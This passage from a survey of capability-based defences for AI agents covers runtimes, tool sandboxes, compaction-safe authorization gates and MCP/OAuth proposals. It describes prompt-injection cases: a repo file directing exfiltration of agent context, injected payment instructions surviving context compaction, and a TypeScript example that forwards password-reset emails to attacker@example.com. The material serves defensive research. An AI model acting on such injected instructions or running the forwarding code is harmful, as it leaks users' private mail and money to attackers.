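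Withdrawing permissions makes an agent less useful. On 37 coding tasks with five runs each, the agent finished 161 of 185 runs with PORTICO and 180 with the fixed list. It finished 21% of runs when it couldn't request anything beyond its initial permissions. In a supplementary test on real Python projects, it succeeded in 31 of 42 cases with PORTICO and in all 42 when grants lasted for the whole task. Some contracts closed a grant too early and had no trusted event to reopen it. The main test on real projects showed no difference, because the agent completed all 14 tasks without a violation under every configuration, including unrestricted access.

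Each grant also takes one extra model turn. A small check with newer models suggests that revocation itself need not reduce the number of tasks they complete. With or without revocation, GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.8 each completed all three tasks, and Gemini 3.5 Flash completed one.

### Agent libOS: agents that change their own tools

PORTICO's contract refers to a known set of tools, but some agents add to their tools as they work. They load packages of instructions, write new tools, start copies of themselves and save their state for reuse. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes an injection that exploits this. A file in a code repository contains instructions for the agent to activate a "debugging" package, register a tool it has generated, send its context to a remote server, and save the result as an image from which later agents will start.

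Agent libOS, built at Tsinghua University, runs each agent as a process, as an operating system runs a program. It is named after library operating systems, which provide operating-system services as a library on top of a small protected layer. Its central rule is that an agent may change what it can request, but doing so does not change what it is authorized to affect.

A capability in Agent libOS is a record that the runtime keeps for a process. It specifies a resource, the rights to that resource, who issued the capability and which capability it derives from. It can also have an expiry time or a limited number of uses. The resource can be a file, a Git repository, a method on a remote server, another process or a channel to the user.

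The operator's software gives a process its first capabilities at launch and can grant more later. When a process creates an object, the runtime can give the process a handle to it. A parent process can pass its rights, or weaker versions of them, to a child process. These routes resemble what object-capability systems call initial conditions, parenthood and endowment.

A process loses a capability when the capability expires, runs out of uses or is revoked by the issuer's side. Restoring a saved state could bring a lost capability back, so before Agent libOS starts a new process from a saved copy, it compares the capabilities in the copy with the current ones. It leaves out any that have been revoked, have expired or have a limited number of uses. If the runtime crashes after sending a refund request, it may be unclear whether the refund went through. The runtime then treats a single-use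 capability as used and doesn't repeat the request automatically.

Before an action runs, several conditions must all hold:

*permitted = active process ∧ capability ∧ task limit ∧ (policy or human approval) ∧ budget*.

A person's approval can't replace a missing capability. A separate check compares the sensitivity of outgoing data with the recipient's clearance. Some data above that clearance can be sent only if a person approves that exact content for that recipient, and each approval is valid for one send.

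In the injection above, the agent might load the package and register the tool. The tool's code can reach the runtime only through one function, `libos.syscall`, which applies the same checks as any other call. If the process has no capability for the remote server, the transmission fails, and an image saved afterwards gives no new right to contact the server.

These records are looser than object capabilities. As with AgentCap, the agent names a resource and the runtime looks for a matching right, so an injection can direct a process to any resource the process already has permission to use. Agent libOS also doesn't confine ordinary programs started outside its checks, such as an MCP server running on the same machine under the operator's account.

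### Scripted tasks and live runs

Zhang tested the enforcement code with 33 scripted tasks, in which no model chose the actions, and all 33 passed. The agents' processes carried out 119 actions, none of them unauthorized, and the runtime refused no legitimate action. The 119 include only actions that ran, so this result doesn't show how many forbidden actions the runtime blocked.

With a simple wrapper around the tools, 20 of 29 actions were unauthorized, but Zhang built that wrapper without the relevant checks. Removing single parts of Agent libOS had much smaller effects. Two of 121 actions were unauthorized when processes didn't have separate memory areas, and one of 120 when child processes could inherit too much. Removing the approval step at the point of action led to no unauthorized actions, so these tasks don't show that it improves security.

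The live test had 12 runs with one model, three in each of four kinds of work. The six runs in a customer portal and a set of research documents contained injected instructions. All 12 runs finished the work safely. However, no undefended agent attempted the same work, so the model may have ignored the injected instructions even without the defense. Six successes are also compatible with a failure rate as high as 39%.

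Zhang makes no claim about how much the runtime slows an agent down. A separate comparison measured the effect of replacing the full list of tools with a short list that the model could expand on demand. The short list cut prompt tokens per task by about a third but raised the number of model calls from 3.7 to 6.6.

### Haven: confining tools that nobody has inspected

Rules about tool calls help only if each tool does what its description says. In their Haven project and the paper *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (2026), Adam, Lu and colleagues at Brown University address tools that do more than they describe. Their example is a tool that writes a file, as advertised, but also reports the file's size to an outside server. A user working on confidential code may not want that information to leave the machine, but the agent has no way to know that the tool sends it.

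Haven analyses the tool's code before it runs and produces a synopsis, a list of the kinds of effect the code can have. In the example, the synopsis shows that the file's content can influence a write to disk and a message to the network. Software on the user's side compares this list with a policy and blocks the call if the policy forbids network access.

Analysis alone is too strict for files. The code could write to any path, because the model supplies the path at run time, so a policy that permits writing only in the project folder would rule the tool out. The tool's developer therefore replaces the ordinary write function with a sandboxed one that accepts limits for each call. The user's software sends those limits with the request:

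1. The user asks for a change to the code, and the policy permits writes in the project folder.
2. The software sends the tool call together with that limit.
3. The sandboxed function checks the actual path and refuses to write anywhere else.

The same analysis checks whether a careless developer has left an unprotected write elsewhere in the tool or altered the limits before they are applied. A user who connects to a remote tool would also need proof that the server is running the code that Haven analysed. The design relies on existing security hardware for that proof.

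Each call has its own limits, so a permission doesn't carry over to the next. But the tool still receives an ordinary path, as ACE's document loader does, rather than a reference to the project folder.

Adam and colleagues tested Haven, a prototype for tools written in Rust. They recorded sessions with two Claude Haiku models and replayed the sessions under different protections. Each of three scenarios had a harmless version and one with an unwanted effect, such as publishing an API key to GitHub. Haven made the right decision in all six cases. Code analysis without the sandboxes was right in five, and a fixed sandbox around the whole server was right in three.

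None of the scenarios was a prompt injection, and the replayed models couldn't respond to a refusal by trying something else. The prototype also assumed it would be given correct policies, which depended on identifying when a file contained a secret. The published results don't include speed measurements.

PORTICO, Agent libOS and Haven were not tested against one another. This is typical of the field. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) surveyed 39 papers and found that researchers almost never compare isolation systems with capability systems on a shared benchmark.

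### When a summary replaces the conversation

PORTICO and Agent libOS keep their grants outside the conversation. Progent has a model derive its rules from the user's request, and the text of that request may be lost in a long session. When a conversation nears the model's length limit, the software running the agent has a model summarize the earlier turns and continues from the summary, which developers call compaction.

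Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in two coding agents, Claude Code and Codex. Each time, the software inserted the summary of the earlier conversation as a user message. After a compaction, a system that checks the latest user message to find out what the user wants will therefore read text written by a model, some of it drawn from documents that strangers supplied.

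In one example, a user asks a banking agent how much they spent in March, and a transaction contains an instruction to pay the attacker. Progent blocks the payment because the user only asked a question. After the conversation is compacted, the summary lists the blocked payment as unfinished work. Progent treats the summary as a new request, writes a rule that permits one payment, to the attacker's account, and enforces that rule correctly.

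When Progent derived new rules after context compaction, attacks succeeded in 31 of 100 cases, compared with 33 without any defence. Progent normally derives its rules once per session, which would avoid this failure, but Fei and colleagues had it derive new rules for each request because the original arrangement works badly in longer sessions. In a test without attacks, the agent finished a second task in 7 of 60 sessions under the first request's rules and in 41 of 60 under new ones.

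The summary's position caused the problem. When the researchers supplied the same kind of summary as a tool result instead, none of 28 policies changed. IntentCap also treats text in the position of a user message as the user's intent, so it may have the same weakness, but this study didn't test it.

Newer models are better at flagging injected instructions when they write summaries. Two of them flagged the instructions in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept the attacker's account or other identifier. But they rarely flag false data. In another test, the user gave the agent their landlord's account number and asked what a notice said. The attacker's notice gave a different account number but contained no instructions. After compaction, the user asked the agent to pay the rent. Rules derived from the summary allowed a payment to the attacker in 290 of 320 cases, and in 59% of cases when the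 stronger GPT-5.5 wrote the rules. Rules derived from the user's own words never allowed such a payment. When an agent acted on the rules derived from the summary, it paid the attacker in 33 of 80 sessions.

Fei and colleagues prove that better summaries can't solve this in general. Let *p_L* be the probability that a system working only from text permits a payment to the account in a legitimate notice, and *p_A* the probability for a forged one. Then

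*p_L − p_A ≤ TV(P_L, P_A)*,

where *P_L* and *P_A* are the distributions of everything the system reads in the two cases. TV, the total variation distance, is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they never overlap. If an attacker imitates real notices perfectly, the distance is 0, and the system accepts the forged account exactly as often as a real one. To do better, it needs information about who wrote the text.

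Even with a prompt designed to keep account numbers out of the summary, the new rules allowed the attacker's payment in 41% of banking cases, mostly because they didn't restrict the recipient.

### Keeping the user's own words

The researchers call their remedy a witnessed-request gate. The agent still reads the summary, but the authorization system, which writes the rules, reads only the user's original messages and the output of tools the developer has chosen to trust.

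The gate attaches a cryptographic tag to each of these messages when it arrives. At compaction, trusted software copies the messages word for word and signs the complete list in order. Before anyone derives new rules from the list, the gate checks the tags to detect forged messages, the order to detect messages an attacker has replayed, and the count to detect missing messages, such as one in which the user cancelled a payment. If a check fails, the agent gets an empty policy and can't call any tool.

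Fei and colleagues ran 40 attacked AgentDojo cases in several arrangements:

| Text used to write the rules | Text the agent reads | Rules that allow the attack | Attacks completed | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Summary | Summary as a user message | 24 | 7 | 9 |
| Latest request only | Summary as a tool result | 0 | 0 | 18 |
| User's messages, through the gate | Summary as a user message | 5 | 0 | 13 |
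| User's messages, through the gate | Summary as a tool result | 6 | 0 | 19 |
| User's messages, through the gate | User's messages only | 2 | 1 | 26 |
| Original request, no compaction | Full conversation | 8 | 2 | 27 |

In these cases, moving the summary into a tool result worked about as well as the gate. The gate's advantage is clearer in the rent example. The latest request says only to pay the rent, and rules based on it never restricted who could be paid. With the gate, the rules included the landlord's account from the user's earlier message, and the gate blocked all 34 attempts by a live agent to pay the attacker.

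The adaptive attacks on the gate tested its code without a live agent. Eight methods of forging, replaying, reordering or removing messages failed in all 608 trials. A simpler filter, which trusts every user message not marked as a summary, matched the gate's results while messages stayed inside one program, but it accepted replayed messages when they passed through a file that the agent could write to. Checking the messages took 0.25 to 0.40 milliseconds per request. These experiments used replayed sessions, and nobody has yet tested the gate inside a commercial agent.

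Other designs are less affected by summaries. In the same study, CaMeL, which attaches permissions to individual values, let the attacker's action through in 3 of 36 banking cases after compaction. Codex's reviewer, Guardian, checks risky calls against the user's messages. OpenAI later changed Guardian to attribute summaries to the assistant. When the researchers planted a false payment request in a saved summary, the version before this change approved 5 of 33 calls and the version after it approved none.

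The gate, like AgentCap and IntentCap, doesn't help when a bill's account number appears only in a stranger's file. It also keeps every request the user has made, including finished ones. A model that writes rules from the whole list could allow a completed payment to be repeated unless another record, such as PORTICO's closing events, shows that the task is over.

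## Products and proposals that use capabilities

Several companies and research groups have described capability designs for agents but have not published attack tests of them. Most of these designs let an agent use an account while other software keeps the password or key. The descriptions are detailed enough to work out which attacks this should stop.

### Code Mode: bindings in place of network access

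Cloudflare, which runs websites and programs for other companies, introduced Code Mode in September 2025. Varda and Pai explain in *Code Mode* that it converts an agent's MCP tools into functions in TypeScript, a typed form of JavaScript. The model gets a single tool, which runs code, and writes a short program that calls as many of the functions as the task needs. They favor this design mainly for performance, since models are trained on far more real code than tool calls, and intermediate results don't have to pass through the model.

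Each program runs in an isolate, a separate instance of Chrome's JavaScript engine, V8, which starts in milliseconds and can be discarded afterwards. The functions that normally open network connections throw errors inside the isolate. The program instead receives bindings, live objects that each give access to one service. A call on a binding goes to a supervisor outside the isolate, which adds the access token and forwards the request to the MCP server. Varda and Pai conclude that an agent "cannot possibly write code that leaks any keys".

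A binding is close to an object capability in the strict sense, because a program can get one only from the supervisor. In *Sandboxing in Cloudflare Workers*, Varda (2025) calls this a "capability-based permissions model" and considers it much easier than filtering network traffic. Pai and Reznykova write in *Project Think*, a 2026 announcement, that the sandbox starts with "almost no ambient authority" and that the developer adds resources one at a time.

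Varda, Pai and Gupta, in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, give the example of a chat room binding with methods to read recent messages, subscribe to new ones and post. None of the methods takes the name of a room, so an agent that holds only this binding can't reach any other room. But the binding doesn't restrict what the agent posts, so an agent that also holds a binding to private files can copy a file into the chat. TACIT's types were designed to catch this kind of flow.

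### A mailbox without its password

Suppose a user asks an agent to find a delivery date in their email and send it to Ana, a colleague. The supervisor keeps the mailbox password and gives the agent's program a binding with two methods:

```typescript
interface Mailbox {
  search(query: string): Promise<Message[]>;
  send(to: string, body: string): Promise<void>;
}
```

One of the emails the agent reads comes from an attacker and contains an instruction to reveal the mailbox password. This attack fails even if the model tries to comply, because the password is not in the model's context or the sandbox, and neither method returns it. The only exception would be if a message in the mailbox contained the password, as an old welcome email might. Cloudflare's documentation page *Code Mode MCP server patterns* tells developers not to expose credentials through tool results, but developers have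 little control over what people have emailed to the user.

The attacker can get private mail without the password. A different injection could lead the model to write this program:

```typescript
const found = await env.MAILBOX.search("password reset");
for (const message of found) {
  await env.MAILBOX.send("attacker@example.com", message.text);
}
```

Both methods belong to the binding, so both calls succeed. The supervisor adds the password, and the mail provider receives ordinary requests from the owner's account. The agent has become a confused deputy while using a reference it rightly holds. Hiding the mail password also doesn't protect the user's other accounts, because an attacker who first requests password resets on them may find the reset links in the forwarded messages.

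Keeping the password hidden still limits the damage. An attacker who steals a password can use it from any computer until the owner changes it, and may be able to lock the owner out. With the binding, the attacker can use only the two methods, and only by getting the agent to call them. The supervisor can also record each call or stop forwarding them.

To prevent the theft of mail, the supervisor can attenuate the binding. It looks up Ana's address before the agent reads any email, and gives the program this object instead:

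```typescript
const taskMailbox = {
  search: (query: string) => mailbox.search(query),
  sendToAna: (body: string) => mailbox.send(anaAddress, body),
};
```

The program now cannot supply an address. A rule that allowed only replies to existing messages would not prevent the leak, because the attacker sent one of those messages and the agent could reply to it with the user's private mail.

The table shows what an injection could achieve with each arrangement, if the agent has no other tools and no email contains the password.

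| What the agent holds | Attacker gets the password | Attacker gets private mail | Ana gets a false date |
|---|---|---|---|
| The mailbox password | Possible | Possible | Possible |
| Binding with `search` and `send` | Blocked | Possible | Possible |
| Binding with `search` and `sendToAna` | Blocked | Blocked | Possible |
| Binding with `search` only | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

The last arrangement blocks all three outcomes because the agent can't contact Ana. The user would have to send the date, and might pass on a false one that the agent took from the attacker's email.

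1Password, which makes a password manager, sells a product that also lets Anthropic's Claude use a login without seeing the password. According to Biometric Update's *Delegated identity stack emerges for AI agents to authenticate, act and pay*, the user approves each login with a biometric check, 1Password fills in the password, and access ends when the task does. The article doesn't present this as an object-capability system. An agent logged in to a mail page can normally write to anyone, so during the task its position is closer to the table's second row than to the third.

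### Bindings that cover too much

Cloudflare's server for its own API gives the agent a much broader binding than the chat room. Describing each API operation as a separate tool would take about 1.17 million tokens, so the server offers only two tools, which take about 1,000. The model uses `search` to look up the operations it needs and `execute` to run code that holds a request function. The code passes a method and a path to this function, and software outside the sandbox adds the credential.

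The request function hides the credential but allows every request the credential permits. The model names each resource with a string, and an injection can change that string. Within the API, the agent therefore has much the same ambient authority as if it held the credential. Cloudflare acknowledges in its documentation that "Code execution does not replace authorization" and tells developers to enforce permissions and approvals in the request function or the tools behind it. Following this advice means writing per-call checks like ScopeGate's.

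Code also makes some existing checks less useful. *DADL* (2026) presents a description language for companies' tools and has its own Code Mode. It points out that an injected prompt may introduce JavaScript that makes unexpected calls. Software that asks for approval one tool at a time would receive a single call to `execute`, with a program as its argument. The supervisor can still check each underlying call as it arrives. DADL's runtime also caps how many of these calls a program can make, which would shorten the forwarding loop in the mailbox example but wouldn't stop its first message.

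The announcement of Project Think describes another way an agent could gain access, which is to write an extension (a program that adds new tools) and declare the permissions the extension needs. The example declares access to GitHub's API and permission to read and write the agent's workspace. An agent under an attacker's influence could declare broad permissions as easily as narrow ones, so the declaration is a limit only if someone else has to accept it. Pai and Reznykova describe no such step. Agent libOS addresses this case explicitly by giving an agent no new authority when it adds a tool.

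The arrangement depends on the isolate. Varda and colleagues concede that security bugs are more common in V8 than in typical hypervisors, the software that separates virtual machines. Cloudflare says it adds a second sandbox, installs security patches within hours and scans code for malicious patterns. In its announcements of Code Mode and the sandbox, the company reports savings in tokens and time, but no attack test.

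### Edera's bounded authorities

Edera, which sells isolation for containers and AI agents, explicitly bases its design on object capabilities. Its November 2026 post *Bounded Authority for AI Agents* starts with an agent that holds a GitHub token. A separate policy allows the agent to write to the repository `project-a`, but the token may cover every repository the developer can use. Anyone who takes over the agent also gets the token.

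In Edera's alternative, the agent holds a capability, written `write(project-a)`, instead of a GitHub token, and doesn't need to know which other repositories exist. Edera calls such capabilities bounded authorities and is applying them to agents and to workloads on Kubernetes, a system for running containers on many machines. In other examples, an agent can make one class of API request without holding the API key, and an MCP server can run only three specified commands.

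The repository example fits the strict definition of an object capability. Edera claims only that this approach limits the damage from a compromise. The claim is reasonable, but the amount of damage still possible varies a great deal between the examples. An injection could still put a back door in `project-a`. A list of three permitted commands may restrict an agent tightly, or hardly at all if it includes a build tool such as `make`. No attack test of Edera's model appears to have been published.

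### Wassette: tools that start with no access

Microsoft's Wassette limits what tools can do. *Introducing Wassette* (2025) describes it as a runtime for components in WebAssembly, a format for programs that run inside a sandbox. An agent can download a component from a public registry and, once the user confirms, call it through MCP. The component can't use files or the network without explicit permission. This follows the design of WASI, a standard interface between WebAssembly programs and the computer that hosts them. According to WASI's *Security*, code under WASI has no ambient authority and can do only what the host grants.

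In Microsoft's example, a user loads a component that fetches web pages and requests a summary of a blog post. Wassette prompts the user to let the component contact `opensource.microsoft.com`, and the component fetches the post after the user agrees. A grammar checker with no network permission couldn't send the user's SSH keys to its developer. Microsoft adds that an attacker would find it difficult to get sensitive data out even if a malicious tool obtained it.

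Like Haven, Wassette mainly protects against tools that do more than advertised. It offers less protection against an injection that redirects the agent, because the agent chooses what data to send even to a component that works as advertised. A component with permission to contact a code-hosting site could publish a secret there if the agent supplied one. The permission covers the whole domain, so it allows posting to an attacker's account as well as the user's.

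Microsoft's *Frequently Asked Questions (FAQ)* calls Wassette's model capability-based, which is accurate for how components start. The term fits the permissions that users see less closely, because these name domains and file paths, and Wassette checks a component's requests against allow and deny lists.

Wassette also asks for permission during the task, when the agent may already have read an attacker's text. Instructions injected into a page could lead the agent to request access to a new domain, and the request would look to the user like part of the work. Microsoft says users may occasionally have to tell the agent to "please fix the permission errors", which could encourage them to treat a blocked request as an error to fix. Many users would probably approve the new domain, given the acceptance rate that Tu and Tu report for another coding agent.

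To adopt Wassette, developers have to rewrite existing MCP servers as WebAssembly components. The user also has to switch off the agent's ordinary tools, as with TACIT and as in the demonstration. Microsoft's announcement reports no attack test.

### What OAuth leaves open

MCP lets an agent connect to an account without the account's password. Its authorization rules use OAuth, a standard in which the user approves access and the agent's software receives a token. Semgrep argues that this determines whether a user may use a server, but not whether a particular operation, prompted by a particular piece of text, should access a particular resource.

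The problem grows with each connection. If a user connects an agent to servers for files, a database, email and a command shell, the agent's authority is the union of all four:

*authority = files ∪ database ∪ email ∪ shell*.

An instruction in an email can then trigger a shell command. The shell server receives the command from a client that the user has approved, with no information about where it originated. MCP's sampling feature also lets a server send the user's software a prompt to run through the model. Semgrep warns that a remote server could use such a prompt to trigger calls to tools on the user's machine. The specification recommends human approval for sampling but doesn't require it.

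This claim is too broad for OAuth in general, because OAuth tokens can have scopes that limit operations, such as permission to read mail but not to send it. The argument is stronger against the usual practice, in which the user approves scopes when connecting a server and those scopes apply to every later task.

Semgrep proposes an extension to A2A, a protocol that agents use to pass tasks to one another. For example, an agent summarising quarterly reports would ask the file server for permission to read one folder until a stated time. The server would issue a token for only those permissions that the agent requested, the server offers and the server's policy allows. Each tool call would name the file and the token, and the server would reject any call that the token doesn't cover. The agent could also derive a narrower token for a helper, such as one that only permits reading a single report.

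Semgrep's design is closer to an object capability than AgentCap's token for each tool call, because the agent has to choose which authority to use. In an example that Semgrep gives without a test, a report contains an instruction to delete all files, and the server refuses because the agent has no capability to delete. This assumes that the hijacked agent doesn't first request one. If it did, the server's policy would have to refuse the request, and the agent itself writes the purpose stated there. The token also doesn't record what prompted a call, so it would still allow the agent to follow an injected instruction to read a different report in the folder.

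In the second phase of the plan for adopting the extension, servers accept tokens but fall back on ambient authority when a call arrives without a token. This is a serious gap, because a hijacked agent could avoid every limit by leaving the token out. Protection begins only in the third phase, when servers reject calls without tokens, and even then the plan keeps broad grants for older services.

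### Tokens tied to an agent's identity

*Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents*, a proposal from Accenture Labs, builds on a draft extension of OAuth, so its designers evidently think OAuth can carry capabilities. Their example is a holiday in Paris for two people from Los Angeles. The user signs a token that gives a coordinating agent, Atlas, a $5,000 budget and permission to delegate. Atlas gives a flight agent, Skyway, a token to reserve seats worth up to $1,500, and other agents get tokens for hotels, restaurants and local transport.

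At first, these agents can only make reservations. After the user approves the complete plan, Atlas revokes their tokens and issues new ones for payment, with more precise amounts. If an injection in a hotel listing misleads the hotel agent, the user has a chance to notice the wrong hotel before the agents can pay for it. The user can also stop everything by revoking Atlas's token, because a service that checks the chain of delegations will find that its first link is no longer valid.

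This design keeps an agent's signing keys in a wallet, a separate program that returns signed results under its own policy, so the agent never holds the keys. The wallet gives the same message for every refusal, so an attacker can't learn the policy by probing it. As with the mailbox binding, the wallet protects the credential, but a hijacked agent can still ask for a signature on anything the policy permits.

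Delegated budgets can add up to more than the original limit. If Atlas gave each of four agents a token for $1,500, every token would be narrower than Atlas's own, but together they would allow $6,000 of spending. A hotel that checks only the token it receives can't detect the excess. *EP Bounded Capabilities* (2026), an individual IETF draft rather than an adopted standard, argues that a signed limit needs a shared, lasting record of what agents have reserved and spent. Without that record, someone could reuse the same token after a retry or a restart.

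Revocation also needs a connection to a central record. A service that verifies tokens offline cannot detect that the user has cancelled one. The Accenture proposal uses an online check in most cases, despite the extra delay.

The Decentralized Identity Foundation's *Delegated Authority Evaluations v1.0 Preview* likewise argues that agents must combine designation with authorization to remove confused deputies, but combining them wouldn't stop a hotel agent from using a valid token to book the hotel an attacker recommends. The Accenture proposal appears to have no published attack test.

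### Network access that is off by default

*Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (Tran, Dhesi and colleagues, 2026) proposes controlling agents at the network. Each agent starts with no permission to contact anything. For each task, a trusted authority issues capabilities that specify a destination, a type of data and a purpose. All the agent's traffic passes through a sidecar, a separate program that can allow a request, remove sensitive parts, refuse it or ask the user. In a similar idea from earlier network research, senders needed a receiver's permission before their traffic could get through.

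A permitted destination isn't suitable for every type of data. Tran and colleagues give the example of medical details, which are appropriate in a health app but not in a restaurant booking. Neither a list of approved hosts nor a plain network capability would distinguish the two cases. They propose checking the sender, the recipient, the task and the data's labels against such norms, outside the agent's control.

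In the mailbox example, the messages to Ana and the attacker both go to the same mail provider, so the sidecar has to read each request and find the recipient to tell them apart. Varda and colleagues object to this kind of filtering in general, because a proxy must fully interpret every API call to decide whether to allow it. They find it easier to write a small wrapper with only the permitted functions. Unlike a wrapper, though, the sidecar also covers an agent whose tools the developer can't change.

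In the design, approved models evaluate requests that fixed rules can't settle. Those models may have to read text that an attacker has influenced, so this part of the check would lack the certainty that Tran and colleagues want from the network. Tran and colleagues leave open how narrow the capabilities should be, and offer the untested architecture as a reference design for further research.

### The capability layer in MCPShield

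In *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents*, Acharya and Gupta (2026) describe MCPShield, an architecture that combines capability-based access control with three other layers of defence: cryptographic proof of a tool's identity, tracking of information flows, and enforcement of a policy at run time. They list 23 kinds of attack on MCP and estimate that no existing defence covers more than 34% of them, while MCPShield would cover 91%.

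That 91% is the share of the listed kinds of attack that the design addresses, which matches 21 of 23, and Acharya and Gupta call it theoretical. It is not comparable with an attack success rate, because a defence can address a kind of attack and still fail against many examples of it. It also weights rare and common attacks equally, so prompt injection through a tool counts as much as restoring an old version of a server.

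The list helps show where capabilities need support. In tool shadowing, a malicious server registers a tool under the same name as a legitimate one, so that the agent calls the wrong tool. A second tool with that name would not affect an agent that held a reference to the legitimate one. In a rug pull, a server changes what a tool does after the user has approved it. A reference doesn't prevent this, because it still leads to the same tool, so MCPShield needs its second layer. Another entry combines a tool that reads files with one that sends email. Defending against this calls for tracking the data that passes between them, as TACIT does.
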